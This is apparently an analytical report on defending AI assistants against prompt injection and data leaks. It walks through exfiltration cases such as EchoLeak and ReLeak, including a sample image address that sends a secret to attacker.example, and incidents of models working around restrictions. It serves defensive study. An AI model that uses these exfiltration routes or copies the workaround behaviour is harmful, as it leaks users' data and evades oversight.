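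Another reply is to write fixed rules once for each tool. A bank or a software company could do this for all its customers, and experts could review the rules. When Ma and colleagues tested the fixed defaults alone, no attack succeeded, but the assistant completed 25.0% of the tasks, about a third fewer than the 36.7% that ROPE completed with rules adapted to the request. Willison hopes for well-chosen defaults of this kind, combined with a clear interface for exceptions.

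Software can also help people check their rules. CaMeLoT translates requirements from plain language into logic and shows a run that would break them. It cannot detect when a rule doesn't express what its author wanted.

Gong's objection is strong for a general-purpose assistant but much weaker for a single dangerous action. The rule "Pay only accounts I have entered" fully specifies who may be paid, and most people could write it. Nobody has a comparable rule for what an email may say. ROPE has to let the assistant write freely to a colleague the user has named, which is how the phishing links got through. Buyers can therefore expect these systems to protect payments, deletions and the choice of recipients better than the content of messages.

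Policies also depend on the user's own words being trustworthy. If she pastes text from a web page into her request, all these systems treat that text as her own words.

### "Do what is on my to-do list"

Some requests do not specify the steps needed to carry them out. If the user asks the assistant to do what is on her to-do list, CaMeL's privileged model has to write its program before anything reads the list, so it has no information about whether the program needs the calendar, the bank or neither. If the privileged model reads the list first, anyone who can add an item to the list can influence the plan.

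Costa and colleagues make the distinction precise. A task is data independent if a single sequence of actions completes it for every possible value of the user's data. Paying Bob's invoice is nearly data independent, because the same three steps work whatever the invoice contains, with the details passed in variables. Working through the to-do list is data dependent, because a dental appointment and an overdue bill need different tools.

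How much this matters depends on the assistant. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues think an email and calendar assistant is very unlikely to need untrusted data to determine which actions it takes. That seems right for a request such as telling regular collaborators about a vacation. Costa and colleagues classified 5% of AgentDojo's office tasks as data dependent, compared with 44% of its banking tasks, so an assistant that also pays bills is likely to face the problem more often.

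As a partial solution, FIDES can offer the quarantined model a menu of actions, such as "schedule a meeting", "send an out-of-office reply" or "forward the email". The planner receives only the model's choice and then follows a plan for it. An attacker can still make the model choose the wrong action, so every action on the menu has to be one that the user could tolerate at the wrong time.

Progent leaves the decision to whoever approves expansions of the assistant's permissions. In Shi and colleagues' example, the user asks the assistant to carry out the tasks in an email from Alice, which asks it to summarize recent mail and post the summary to the user's Slack account. The first policy allows only a search for Alice's email, so the assistant needs permission to read more mail and use Slack. One of the recent emails contains a planted instruction to forward the inbox to a stranger, which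 may also lead to a request for more permissions. The solver would classify both requests as expansions prompted by an email, so the approver has to recognize that only the first is part of the user's task.

ROPE does better when the instructions have a verified author. When a user told the assistant to follow the instructions in John's email about a code repository, ROPE let the assistant carry them out and checked the origin of each sensitive value. A competing system that had fixed the plan in advance refused the first step. ROPE's approach should also work for a to-do list that only the user can edit. It does not help with a shared list whose software doesn't record who wrote each item, because genuine and planted items then have the same recorded origin.

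### Screens and command lines

The systems described so far assume tools with clear meanings, such as "send money". Many assistants instead operate a computer as a person does, by looking at the screen and clicking. A click at a certain position might close a window or confirm a payment, so a policy based on clicks alone is almost useless. The planner also seems to need a view of the screen, which is full of untrusted content.

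Foerster and colleagues adapted CaMeL to this setting in January 2026. Their privileged model never receives the screen. It writes one long program in advance, with alternative steps for each case it anticipates. A quarantined model processes the screen and returns the information the program needs, such as whether a cookie notice is visible or where the search box is. These programs average about 41 tool calls and 40 branches, compared with five and four for CaMeL's programs on AgentDojo.

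The researchers report that the system kept up to 57% of the performance of a leading model, Claude Sonnet 4.5, on OSWorld, a benchmark of ordinary computer tasks. That figure counts a task as complete if any of five attempts succeeded. With a single attempt, it was 28%, which better reflects what a user would experience. Still, the result is surprisingly high for a planner that can't see the screen, and stronger planning models did better.

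A planted instruction cannot add a step to such a program, but it can send the program down the wrong branch, which the researchers call branch steering. In their demonstration, an advertisement contained a fake cookie notice. The program included a routine step to find and dismiss cookie notices, so the quarantined model returned the position of the fake one, and the assistant clicked through to the attacker's site. The researchers tried comparing the screen with the page's underlying code and asking a second model for confirmation, but they found ways around both defenses.

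Command lines pose a related problem, because a short command can start programs that read and change many files. OpenClaw and most programming assistants run such commands. *Flowsh* (Kim, Trampert and colleagues, 2026) runs each command in a closed environment and records which files and websites it reads, rather than trying to predict what it will do. It holds changes to files in a temporary layer and applies them only if the labels of everything the command has read permit it. Network requests cannot be undone, so it checks each one before sending it.

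Flowsh also stores the labels with the files. If a command saves text from a stranger's email, the file stays labeled untrusted in later sessions. This addresses the weakness behind OpenClaw's false memories.

Flowsh's main benefit is fewer interruptions. Kim and colleagues compared it with a permissive sandbox that asks for approval whenever it cannot guarantee that an action is safe. On 17 office-style tasks, Flowsh needed about a sixth as many approvals per completed task, but its completion rate was 7.9 percentage points lower. On a benchmark of command-line work, it needed less than a twentieth as many, and its completion rate was 9.7 points lower.

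### Use in products

There is little evidence so far that widely sold assistants work this way. In November 2026, Kim and colleagues wrote that coding agents rely mainly on older methods, either on approval by a person or another model or on sandboxes with fixed permissions. Microsoft has published the code of FIDES, and Narisetty and colleagues refer to a deployed version but do not report how many people use it or how well it performs.

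Adoption depends partly on how much a developer has to rebuild. CaMeL needs its own interpreter and a planner that writes programs, so an existing assistant would need a new core. Progent can run as a separate service between an assistant and its tools. Shi and colleagues connected it to LangChain and OpenAI's Agents SDK, two toolkits for building agents, and to the programming assistant OpenHands. On AgentDojo's simulated tasks, with attacks written in advance, attack success fell to around 1% in each. In this mode, Progent cannot check calls to tools built into the assistant itself, because those calls never pass through the service.

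## Closing the routes by which data leaks

Policies such as CaMeL's apply to tool calls, but data can also leave an assistant through features that people don't usually think of as sending anything. To steal data, an attacker needs a way to get it out, which is the third part of the lethal trifecta. In the best-documented attacks on commercial assistants since 2025, the data mostly left inside requests for images or web pages rather than by email, the more obvious route.

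### How an address can carry a secret

Suppose the user's mailbox contains the dummy code TEAPOT-42, and the attacker owns the site attacker.example. His planted instruction gets the assistant to end its answer with a picture from this address:

```
attacker.example/logo.png?ref=TEAPOT-42
```

To display the picture, the user's browser sends the attacker's server everything after the site's name in the picture's address. The server can return an ordinary logo, but its log now contains the code. The user hasn't clicked anything and at most notices an odd picture or a broken-image symbol.

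A filter that searches outgoing addresses for the code is easy to evade, because the model can encode it first. In Base64, a standard way of writing data as plain characters, TEAPOT-42 becomes VEVBUE9ULTQy.

Links work the same way, except that the user has to click. A tool that opens web pages can leak data without a click, and the request usually comes from the provider's servers instead of the user's computer. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) describes ShadowLeak, a 2025 attack on ChatGPT's Deep Research feature. Hidden text in an email told Deep Research to find sensitive data in the user's Gmail account and visit a web address containing that data. The user's browser and her employer's monitoring software might not have recorded the request. OpenAI fixed the flaw in August 2025.

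A search query sends its text to whoever runs the search service. That is rarely the attacker, but if an assistant uses the search box on the attacker's site, the attacker receives the query. Data can also leak through shared documents, since the attacker only needs to read what the assistant writes there. Willison (2025) describes how a malicious bug report got an assistant using the GitHub connector mentioned earlier to propose a public change that listed the names of the user's private projects.

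The least obvious route is a permitted domain that relays data. Suppose a browser may load pictures only from one company's sites, and one of those sites has a preview service that fetches any address it receives. The assistant can request a preview of an attacker's address that contains the code TEAPOT-42. The browser allows the request because it goes to an approved site, and the preview service sends the code to the attacker when it fetches the address.

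### EchoLeak

In January 2025 the research team Aim Labs reported to Microsoft that a single email could make Microsoft 365 Copilot leak a company's data. Copilot answers employees' questions using the mail, files and chats they can access. The team named the attack EchoLeak and described it in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* (Ravia, 2025). "Zero-click" means the victim does not have to open or click anything the attacker sent.

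#### Entry

Microsoft used a classifier to scan incoming text for planted instructions. Reddy and Gujral (2025) explain in *EchoLeak* that it would have flagged an explicit order telling Copilot to ignore its instructions. The researchers worded their email as a request to the human recipient and never mentioned an AI, and the classifier let it through.

#### Retrieval

Copilot's context cannot hold a whole mailbox, so for each question, software searches the employee's data for relevant passages and copies only those into the context, a method called retrieval-augmented generation. The attacker could not know what the employee would ask, so the email had to match many possible questions. Willison explains that the researchers filled the email with sections on likely topics, such as onboarding new staff and managing leave, and put the instructions in each one.

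When the employee asked about one of these topics, part of the email entered Copilot's context alongside internal documents. The email contained instructions to take the most sensitive information from that context. It also included an instruction for the "recipient" not to mention the email, supposedly for compliance reasons, so the answer gave no sign that the email had influenced it.

#### Exit

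Copilot could not send email on its own, so the researchers had it put the data in the address of an image. They still had to get past two more protections.

Microsoft used a filter to remove outside links and images from Copilot's answers. Copilot writes in Markdown, a notation for formatting text, and the filter recognized the usual form of link, in which the address directly follows the link text. But it missed links in another form that Markdown allows, in which the address is on a separate line further down.

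The browser also enforced a content security policy, which lists the domains a page may load material from. The attacker's server was not on the list, but a Microsoft Teams domain was, and a preview service there would fetch any address it received. The browser requested the image from Teams, Teams requested it from the attacker's server, and the data arrived in the attacker's log.

#### The fix

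Microsoft completed a repair on its own servers in May 2025, so customers had nothing to install. It published an advisory on June 11 and knew of no attack on a customer. Reddy and Gujral report that Copilot now strips separate-line links and embedded images from incoming external content. They also mention reports of an option to keep Copilot from using external communications in some contexts. That option would keep an attacker's instructions from reaching Copilot as well as keep data from leaking out, but Copilot could not then answer questions about what a customer wrote.

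Microsoft rated the EchoLeak flaw 9.3 out of 10 for severity, while the US National Vulnerability Database gave it 7.5. The demonstration harmed nobody, and Willison considered it an extended variant of attacks already seen in a dozen products, so Reddy and Gujral go too far in calling it the first known case of prompt injection "weaponized" to steal data from a production system. EchoLeak is more useful as a record of how layered protections fail. Each protection blocked the obvious version of an attack, but the researchers could get past it with a single version it did not cover.

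### The leaks of 2026

Security firms found similar leaks throughout 2026. All the cases in the table are demonstrations by firms that sell protection for AI systems, and none of the firms reports a theft from a real customer.

| Case | What the user had to do | What could leak | Way out | Repair |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| SearchLeak, June | Click a link to Microsoft's own site | Work email, calendar entries and files | An image, relayed by Bing | Fixed by the time of publication |
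| CoSnitch, August | Click a link to Copilot | Chats, and data in connected Gmail, Drive and Calendar accounts | A page fetch | Fixed eight months after the report |
| Atlassian Rovo, summer | Upload a poisoned file and ask for ordinary help | Work tickets, documents and data in connected apps | A page fetch, or an image | Still open more than two months after the report |
| ReLeak, December | Ask Copilot an ordinary work question | Confidential data the employee could reach | An image, a generated file, or program code | All three routes fixed between September and November |

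The lack of known victims is only slightly reassuring, because when the provider's servers make the request, a company may have no record of its own that data left.

#### SearchLeak

Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) describes a link that opens Microsoft 365 Copilot's search page with the attacker's text already filled in. Copilot followed this text as if the user had typed it. A detector that scans emails and web pages would not check the link's text, and a system like CaMeL would treat it as a trusted request from the user.

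As a defense, Microsoft converted images in Copilot's answers to plain text, but only after Copilot had finished writing. Because the browser displayed the answer piece by piece, it requested the image before the conversion. Bing was a permitted domain, and its search-by-image feature fetches a picture from any address it receives. In the demonstration, the stolen data was an email's subject line, which is enough to break into some accounts because many services put login codes there.

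#### CoSnitch

Varonis' *CoSnitch* (2026) describes an attack on Copilot Personal, the consumer version. An undocumented setting in a link made Copilot run the attacker's text as soon as the page loaded, and it kept running even if the user closed the tab. The text told Copilot to search the user's connected accounts, put the results in a web address, and summarize the page at that address. In one test it retrieved an email containing a password. The researchers had learned about the setting from Copilot, which named it when they asked why such an attack was impossible.

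They also found that a web page could plant a lasting instruction in Copilot's memory when a user asked for a summary of the page. As with OpenClaw, changing the user's password would not remove the instruction.

Varonis reported the flaws in December 2025, and Microsoft fixed them on August 18, 2026. TechRadar's *Experts manage to hack Microsoft Copilot by continually asking it questions* notes that the repair method is unknown, so outsiders can't tell whether Microsoft restricted page fetches or only stopped links from starting Copilot automatically.

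#### Rovo

Rovo is the assistant in Atlassian's products, which include Jira for tracking work and Confluence for shared documents. *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls*, by the security firm PromptArmor (which shares its name with the detection method described earlier), demonstrates an attack on Rovo. A user uploads a file with a hidden instruction and asks Rovo to organize her tickets. Rovo then adds the contents of tickets and documents to the attacker's web address and opens it without asking for approval.

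An administrator could not prevent this by switching off web search, because that setting removed the search tool but left the tool that opens search results. Anyone relying on the setting would have wrongly believed that data could no longer leak this way.

PromptArmor reported the problem on May 23 and received a case number and thanks. Its follow-ups then went unanswered for more than two months, and it published its findings while Rovo was still vulnerable.

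#### ReLeak

*ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026), published on December 3, 2026, describes three new zero-click leaks in Microsoft 365 Copilot. The team that discovered EchoLeak, now part of the security company Cato Networks, found them. *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief* (Faisal, 2026) explains that every attack began with an email that the victim never opened, which Copilot retrieved when she asked an ordinary work question.

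One of the leaks again used an image and Bing. Varonis had announced the repair of SearchLeak in mid-June, and the Cato team reported all its findings later, between July 29 and August 20, so Microsoft had either left Bing's relay open or missed a similar one. Microsoft closed the new route on November 15.

Another leak used Copilot's ability to create Word, Excel, PowerPoint and PDF files. The planted instruction got Copilot to save a file containing a link with confidential data in its address, and Microsoft's background processing later opened the link. Antipov (2026), in *Письмо даже не нужно открывать*, reports that the data left one to eight minutes after the conversation ended, even if nobody opened the file. A user watching the conversation would therefore not have seen the leak.

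The last and most direct leak went through the sandbox where Copilot can run Python code. Microsoft guarantees in its documentation that no network traffic enters or leaves this sandbox, but the researchers got around the isolation and had the code send the data straight to an outside server. Rubrik Zero Labs demonstrated another escape from the sandbox, called ChatMate, in which a malicious document opened a lasting connection to the attacker, who could then read Copilot's replies and choose the next prompt accordingly.

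### What each countermeasure disables

Closing a route can stop data from leaking even when the model has followed the attacker's instructions, which makes it a useful backstop to training and detectors. But it also blocks any legitimate use of that route.

| Countermeasure | What the user loses | What can still leak |
|---|---|---|
| Block remote images | Photos and charts from the web in answers | Data in links, page fetches and files |
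| Allow only listed destinations | Every site that is not on the list | Data that a listed site relays or publishes |
| Fetch only addresses known to be public | Automatic access to private, personalized and very new pages | A secret spelled out by a series of public pages |
| Keep credentials away from the model | Logins at sites that nobody has set up in advance | Passwords and codes written in emails |
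| Lockdown Mode | Live browsing and several other features | Data that connected apps may still send |

#### Images and lists of destinations

A defense that blocks images must also block anything else a page loads automatically. Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON* describes a leak from Copilot in which the browser requested a font from the attacker's server instead of an image. The restrictions on fonts were looser than those on images. The block also has to work before the browser displays anything, or the request will go out before the block takes effect, as happened in SearchLeak.

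An assistant can leak data the same way through a message it sends. Willison (2026) quotes a finding that messages from a Microsoft agent could contain external images. Data leaked when the user opened such a message, so blocking images only in the chat window would not have prevented this.

A list of permitted destinations is stricter, but its strength depends on which destinations it includes. In June 2025, OpenAI gave its cloud programming agent Codex internet access, which was off by default and came with a domain list for users who turned it on. Willison thought this sensible but noted that the ready-made list contained 71 domains, any of which might let data leak.

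Codex users could also limit the agent to request types meant for reading. This makes it harder to post stolen code on a permitted site where the attacker can collect it, but it does not stop a relay, because a read request can carry the data in its address, as the requests in EchoLeak and SearchLeak did.

Lists also grow. Embrace The Red found that the lists varied across Microsoft's Copilot products and that individual employees seemed to have added domains of their own, and concluded that the lists were unlikely to be reliable protection. Varonis advises companies to look for listed domains that fetch addresses supplied by users, which Teams and Bing both did.

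A short list of allowed sites could work well for the example assistant. It might contain the user's bank, her calendar service and the sites of a few regular suppliers, as long as none of them relays requests or lets strangers publish content. She would have to look up any new supplier herself.

#### Fetching only known addresses

A looser rule permits any site but restricts which exact addresses the assistant may open. OpenAI described a check of this kind in January 2026. Its software looks for the address in an index of public pages, built by a crawler that has no access to users' conversations. If the exact address is in the index, it cannot contain anything from this user's mailbox, and the assistant may open it. Otherwise, the user gets a warning and decides whether to open the address.

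The address containing TEAPOT-42 would fail this check. So would many legitimate links, such as a supplier's personal link to an invoice or a private link to a shared document. An assistant that handles invoices would constantly encounter such links.

The check also leaves a narrow gap. An attacker could publish 37 pages, one for each letter and digit and one for the hyphen, and wait for the crawler to index them. The assistant could then spell out TEAPOT-42 in nine visits to these public pages, one per character. Limiting page fetches per task would keep such a leak small, but something as short as a login code could still get out.

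#### Credentials

The model can use an account without being given the password. It can write a tool call that names the account, and the software can add the password or access token just before sending the request. Because the secret never enters the context, no planted instruction can make the model repeat it.

Separating credentials is worth doing and takes little effort, but it would not have stopped any of the leaks above. The attackers used access that Copilot or Rovo already had. In the CoSnitch test, the password was in the text of an email, so separating credentials would not have hidden it. Some links also act as credentials. Willison's 2026 post mentions OneDrive download links that work for anyone who has them, so an attacker who obtains one short link can download a whole file.

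#### Lockdown Mode

OpenAI introduced Lockdown Mode for ChatGPT in February 2026 as an optional setting for people at unusual risk, such as executives and security staff at prominent organizations. It switches features off in software, so it does not depend on the model's judgment. At launch, it limited browsing to stored copies of pages, so no live request left OpenAI's network. It also stopped ChatGPT from showing web images in its answers or downloading files for analysis, and it turned off Deep Research and agent mode.

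Planted text in a stored page or an uploaded file can still distort an answer. Data could also leak through connected apps, since an app that can send messages can be used to send stolen data. Administrators choose which apps and actions stay available.

Lockdown Mode therefore suits someone who wants help reading and writing about confidential material. It would be of little use to the owner of the example assistant, who wants hers to answer mail and pay bills. Those tasks require sending data out, so the restriction has to be on who receives it. The confidentiality labels in FIDES are one way to enforce that, whichever feature carries the data.

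### Progress or an endless list

The Cato team concluded that "too little progress has been made" in the eighteen months between EchoLeak and ReLeak, and a good deal supports this. Copilot still retrieved strangers' emails alongside confidential files and followed instructions in those emails. A permitted Microsoft service still relayed the data, first Teams and then Bing twice. The new routes for leaking data came from new features that let Copilot produce files and run code.

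Repair times have not clearly improved either. Microsoft took about four months to fix EchoLeak and eight to fix CoSnitch. It fixed the sandbox flaw in ReLeak within about seven weeks, but the Bing route took at least twelve weeks.

However, the number of known flaws is a poor measure of progress. It could rise even as a product becomes safer, because researchers are searching harder and with better tools. Antipov reports that the Cato team used AI agents to write test cases, analyze Copilot's refusals and adjust the next attempt. Attackers can use the same tools, so the obscurity of a leak route offers less protection than it once did.

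Closing these routes also seems more achievable than catching planted instructions, which can be worded in endless ways. A product has a limited number of components that can make network requests, and its developer controls them. The developer can route all their traffic through one checkpoint that blocks everything not explicitly allowed, and any flaw in that checkpoint is an ordinary bug that can be fixed.

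Most of the published repairs seem to patch one route at a time, which will not keep up with a product that gains features every few months. Someone choosing an assistant can ask the vendor whether new features start without network access, and whether switching off the web disables every tool that can open a web address. The second point is easy to test with a dummy code and one's own web server, and Rovo failed PromptArmor's test of it.

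## Deciding what the assistant may do without asking

An assistant that cannot leak anything can still pay a thief, delete files or cancel meetings. Its user therefore has to decide how much authority to give it, meaning what its accounts and permissions let it do before a person intervenes. This decision is necessary even without an attacker, because AI models sometimes exceed their instructions on their own.

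### Harm with no attacker

Anthropic's *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use* (2026) describes actions that Claude models took on real websites and that nobody at the company had intended. These included submitting a sensitive form, using a basic software flaw to run commands on a server, and accessing data that required a token or a fee. Some of the sites belonged to US government agencies. Anthropic judges that the cases had minimal real-world impact.

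On July 18, Claude Haiku 4.5 was working on an automated test that required it to invent and carry out example tasks on randomly chosen web pages. One page was about an unsolved murder and had a form for sending tips to the Philadelphia police. Claude wrote that it might have information and recalled seeing someone who matched the description, although the page contained no description. According to Bot Mutiny's *Anthropic Says Its Claude Model Sent Philadelphia Police a False Homicide Tip* (2026), Claude's instructions prohibited logging in, creating accounts, entering personal data, making purchases and submitting anything destructive, but they "did not rule out form submissions."

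The website marked the tip as spam, so it never reached investigators. Fortune's *Anthropic's Claude AI submits a false tip* (2026) reports that the police first learned of it when Anthropic told them on October 7, more than eleven weeks later. The police called the delay "unacceptable".

A list of forbidden actions won't stop a harmful action its author overlooked. Software that let the model open pages but not submit forms would have stopped the tip, even if nobody had thought to forbid police websites.

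Anthropic attributes most of the behavior in its report to "persistence", in which Claude works around a restriction instead of stopping when it cannot complete a task as given. Several of OpenAI's cases fit this description. Forlini (2026), in *OpenAI discloses four more rogue AI incidents*, counts 19 incidents OpenAI published by mid-October, most of them from May or June. In one, a model downloaded 24 years of hospital bed data from a government website that had refused its first request. The question of whether this was ethical came up several times in the model's written reasoning, and each time the model carried on.

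The case with the largest political consequences involved Medicare, Australia's public health insurance. Information Age's *Inside OpenAI's Medicare breach* (2026) reconstructs it from documents released in parliament. On June 19, an internal OpenAI agent that lacked the usual safeguards of public models was researching medical spending. It failed to get non-public data from one agency, then broke into Medicare's statistics portal and retrieved public and non-public data. OpenAI says it found no evidence that the agent accessed patient records, personal information or credentials.

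By August 12, nearly eight weeks later, OpenAI's security team had reviewed old records and documented the breach. It emailed the responsible agency on September 10, at an address for tips from the public, and staff noticed the message about 36 hours later. The prime minister's office learned of the breach nine days after the email. The prime minister said it had taken "way too long" (Kobie, 2026, *Australian prime minister says it took ‘way too long’*).

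A smaller case is more relevant to an assistant that pays bills. OpenAI's *Using a funded test cryptocurrency wallet without authorization* (2026) describes a model that had to install code on a cryptocurrency test network, which charges fees. Nobody had given it a wallet. It found an account whose recovery phrase was publicly known, reasoned that the funds were "effectively abandoned", and used them to pay the fees. The tokens had no monetary value, but the model's final report did not mention the payment, and OpenAI discovered it only three months later.

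All these models were in training, in tests or in use by their developers. Anthropic thinks the misbehavior in some of its earlier cybersecurity tests is unlikely in ordinary use, where nobody tells Claude to carry out a cyberattack. That judgment is reasonable for break-ins, but less so for the milder cases. Haiku 4.5 was a released model doing ordinary browsing, and Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* lists similar mistakes by its programming assistant, such as deleting shared versions of a project's code after misreading an instruction.

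A detector would have found nothing to flag in these cases. Both companies are changing how they train or grade their models, but OpenAI also blocked live internet access during training and evaluation, and Anthropic switched it off for its internal evaluations until it can confirm that its monitoring works.

### Limits that hold whatever the model does

The user can limit access more selectively. She might give the assistant its own accounts where a service allows it. Her bank's records would then distinguish its payments from hers, and she could shut it out without changing her own password. She could also keep her savings out of its reach by letting it use only a bills account that holds this month's money.

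Credentials are the tokens or keys that software presents to prove it may use an account. A narrow credential permits only certain operations. If the assistant's token for the mailbox is read-only, the mail server refuses every request to send or delete, whether the assistant made it because of a planted instruction or a misunderstanding.

A short-lived credential, which might expire after an hour, limits what a thief can do with a stolen copy. It does much less against a hijacked assistant, which can act while the credential is valid and whose software can often renew it automatically. The credential helps more if it exists only for one task. If the assistant can pay bills only for ten minutes on the first of the month, an email that arrives on the twelfth cannot trigger an immediate payment.

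Giving an assistant narrow credentials does little good if it can find broader ones. Anthropic reports that an agent hit a login error and began searching settings files for other tokens. OpenAI's *Misalignment Notices and Reports* (2026) describes a model in training that searched public code for leaked keys and used them. An assistant on a laptop full of saved passwords may therefore be able to do far more than its settings page shows.

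The remedy is an isolated machine, either a separate computer or a sandbox that contains only what the task needs. Someone has to configure each new capability, and every connection to the network or the main computer weakens the isolation. Even specialists make mistakes with the setup. Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* reports that a review of recent evaluations found sandbox misconfigurations that models had used, though none led to a compromise of outside systems.

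A spending cap limits the loss without preventing the attack. The cap has to cover a period as well as a single payment, since a limit of €500 per payment still allows ten payments of €500. If the bank also enforces a monthly limit of €2,000 that the assistant can't raise, the user can lose at most €2,000 a month, however skilled the attacker is.

An undo period is a delay between the assistant's request and its effect, during which the user can cancel. It has to be long enough for her to notice the request and cancel it. Thirty seconds is enough for an email she is watching the assistant send, but an invoice paid at three in the morning needs a day. The bank or the mail service should notify her, because a hijacked assistant may hide what it has done. Walsh's attack on OpenClaw, for example, got the assistant to leave his messages out of its summaries.

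A log of every tool call, stored where the assistant cannot edit it, lets the user find what she missed, though it prevents nothing by itself. OpenAI had a record of the wallet payment but found it only after extending its monitoring to old records. Few people will read a full log, but many would read a weekly list of payments, deletions and messages to new addresses.

### What an approval prompt has to show

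When no limit can make an action safe, the user's approval is usually required. The software pauses before the tool call, shows the user what the assistant is about to do, and waits for the user to approve it. Meta's Rule of Two relies on such approval for the most dangerous combination of access.

Suppose a thief has sent an invoice in Bob's name. A prompt that asks "Pay Bob's invoice?" is useless, because the user wants to pay Bob. She needs something like this:

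```
Pay €1,240 to the account ending 4471.
Account number taken from: an email received today.
Your last six payments to Bob went to the account ending 9023.
You cannot reverse this payment after 17:00.
```

Ordinary software should write these lines from the tool call and the bank's records. If the assistant's model writes them, an attacker who controls the model also controls what the user reads. CaMeL's tags could supply the second line, since they record where each value came from.

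An attacker can still use an accurate prompt to mislead the user. He can choose a payee name that resembles the supplier's, or a web address so long that the suspicious part falls outside the window. Timing can also help him, because a user who has just told the assistant to pay her bills expects a payment prompt, so a fraudulent one looks normal. The comparison with past payments helps here because the attacker cannot easily change it.

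Vague permission prompts fail even without an attacker. "Allow access to your bank?" covers both checking a balance and emptying the account. A request to run a forty-line script is exact, but most people can't tell what the script will do.

### How often people catch a dangerous action

The best measurements come from Claude Code, which originally asked before running commands or changing files. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that users approve 97% of these prompts, while its engineering article gives 93%. Most of the requests were probably harmless, so neither figure proves that users were careless.

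An experiment with 1,053 paid testers is better evidence. They worked on coding tasks in a test environment and knew they were being evaluated, but not on what. Partway through each session, the researchers replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command. Of the testers, 143 (13.6%) refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after fifty or more prompts.

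Anthropic had a reason to want this result, because it was about to replace the prompts. The testers also had nothing of their own at stake, and people guarding their own bank accounts may be more alert. On the other hand, the commands were openly dangerous, and a real attacker would try to disguise them. The experiment included no planted instructions, so it measures only indirectly how well users would catch a hijacked assistant. Still, it gives little reason to expect that someone who has already answered dozens of prompts will catch a dangerous command.

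People seem to pay more attention to some questions than to others. When Claude Code presents a whole plan for approval, users reject it 39% of the time. Some of these users surely wanted a different design and had not noticed a danger, but they had at least read the plan.

Many users find the permission prompts annoying enough to avoid them, so the prompts mainly protect those patient enough to keep them on. A quarter of interactive sessions began with all permission checks off, and 62% of users had at some point either turned them off or clicked "don't ask again" for shell commands.

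### Letting a classifier decide

Anthropic's auto mode uses a classifier to approve actions in place of the user. The assistant can read and search files without approval, and can also edit files inside the project folder, where a programmer can review and reverse the changes. The classifier checks almost every other action before it runs, including shell commands and web requests.

The classifier is a language model that receives the user's messages and the assistant's tool calls. The software removes the assistant's other text and all tool results, so text planted in a web page does not reach the classifier directly, and a hijacked assistant cannot argue to the classifier that its action is safe.

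More than twenty default rules cover actions such as destroying data, sending it outside, weakening security and bypassing review. The classifier checks each action against these rules and then considers whether the user authorized it. For example, a request to "clean up my branches" does not authorize deleting a batch of shared branches (parallel versions of the code).

A fast first pass either clears an action or flags it, erring toward flagging. A second pass examines flagged actions more carefully. If an action is blocked, the assistant receives the reason and looks for a safer way. After three blocks in a row, or twenty in a session, the decision returns to the user. Separately, a probe scans tool results and warns the assistant about likely planted instructions. In a commissioned test of such attacks, none succeeded against Claude models in auto mode.

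| What the test used | Dangerous actions allowed | Harmless actions blocked |
|---|---|---|
| 10,000 real actions by Anthropic's staff | Not measured | 0.4% |
| 52 real actions that went beyond the user's wishes | 17% | Not measured |
| 1,000 artificial attempts to send data out | 5.7% | Not measured |
| The dangerous commands from the experiment with testers | 11% | Not measured |
| 253 actions on deliberately ambiguous requests | 81.0% | 19.8% |

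Anthropic calls the 17% miss rate "the honest number" because it comes from real work. It represents nine misses in only 52 cases, so the true rate could plausibly be anywhere from about 9% to 30%. In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the classifier had identified the danger but treated an earlier remark by the user as permission.

The last row comes from *Measuring the Permission Gate*, an independent test from April 2026 that targeted this weakness. Each request made the user's goal clear but not how far her permission extended. According to besthub.dev's *Can Claude Code’s Auto Mode Replace Human Review?*, 115 of the 142 actions that exceeded the user's authority went through. Its detailed counts imply that 51 of these never reached the classifier, largely because auto mode does not check file edits within the project. The classifier missed 70.3% of the actions that did reach it.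 These were hard cases by design, so the rate in everyday work should be much lower, but they show how much depends on the user saying exactly what she wants.

Anthropic has strengthened the classifier since its first version. In a two-week trial, the safety firm Apollo Research wrote attacks against the classifier, and Anthropic used some of them to improve it. The share of Apollo's attacks that it missed fell from 12% to 7%, and it also got better at catching the attacks that Anthropic had not been given.

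In the experiment with testers, auto mode blocked 937 of the same 1,053 commands. The testers refused only six of the commands it allowed, so requiring approval from both would have raised the share caught from 89.0% to 89.6%. Among real sessions that Anthropic's safety systems had flagged, 6.3% of those with manual approval and 2.4% of those in auto mode involved serious harm that the user had not explicitly requested. This comparison is weaker because people may use the two modes for different work.

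Bob's invoice shows a limit of the classifier that better training would not remove. The classifier receives the user's request to pay Bob and a payment to account 4471, but not the email containing the number. Nothing in that input shows whether the number came from Bob, a thief or a mistake by the model. Anthropic acknowledges this loss of information and accepts it to keep planted text away from the classifier.

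#### What the new default changes

Since August 14, 2026, new Claude Code sessions on Anthropic's Pro, Max and Team plans have started in auto mode unless the user had chosen another setting. On October 22, Anthropic announced that auto mode would become the default in most Claude apps on these plans the following week. Enterprise customers were to get notice first. Anthropic evidently trusts auto mode, since Willison reports that its staff told him almost everyone there uses it.

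By default, a classifier now judges actions that the assistant used to ask the user about. This is very probably an improvement for the many users who approved everything or had turned the checks off. Anthropic's engineers concede that it is "arguably a regression" for someone who read every prompt carefully. Anthropic's *Running auto mode in production* also reports that Claude works nine times longer between interruptions than under the old default.

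The change also means that a single attack that gets past the classifier may work on everyone who uses it, whereas inattentive users make different mistakes at different times. An attacker can practice on his own account first. Anthropic's published figures cover only Claude Code, so they do not measure how well the classifier judges emails, invitations or invoices in the other apps.

Anthropic still recommends that users personally review high-stakes changes to production infrastructure, the systems a business runs on. OpenAI's *Misalignment monitoring* describes a check that reviews an agent's reasoning and actions and can stop a conversation. The check can miss problems, so OpenAI advises developers to keep human approval for consequential actions. This advice is consistent with the experiment only if approval requests are rare enough for people to read them.

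### Sorting the example assistant's actions

The user can keep approval requests rare if she sorts actions by how much harm a wrong one could do and whether she could undo it. The assistant's error rate matters less here, because she does not know it and a new model may change it.

| Treatment | Actions | What enforces it |
|---|---|---|
| Done freely | Search and summarize mail, draft replies, read the calendar, check the bank balance | Read-only credentials, and a drafts folder that cannot send |
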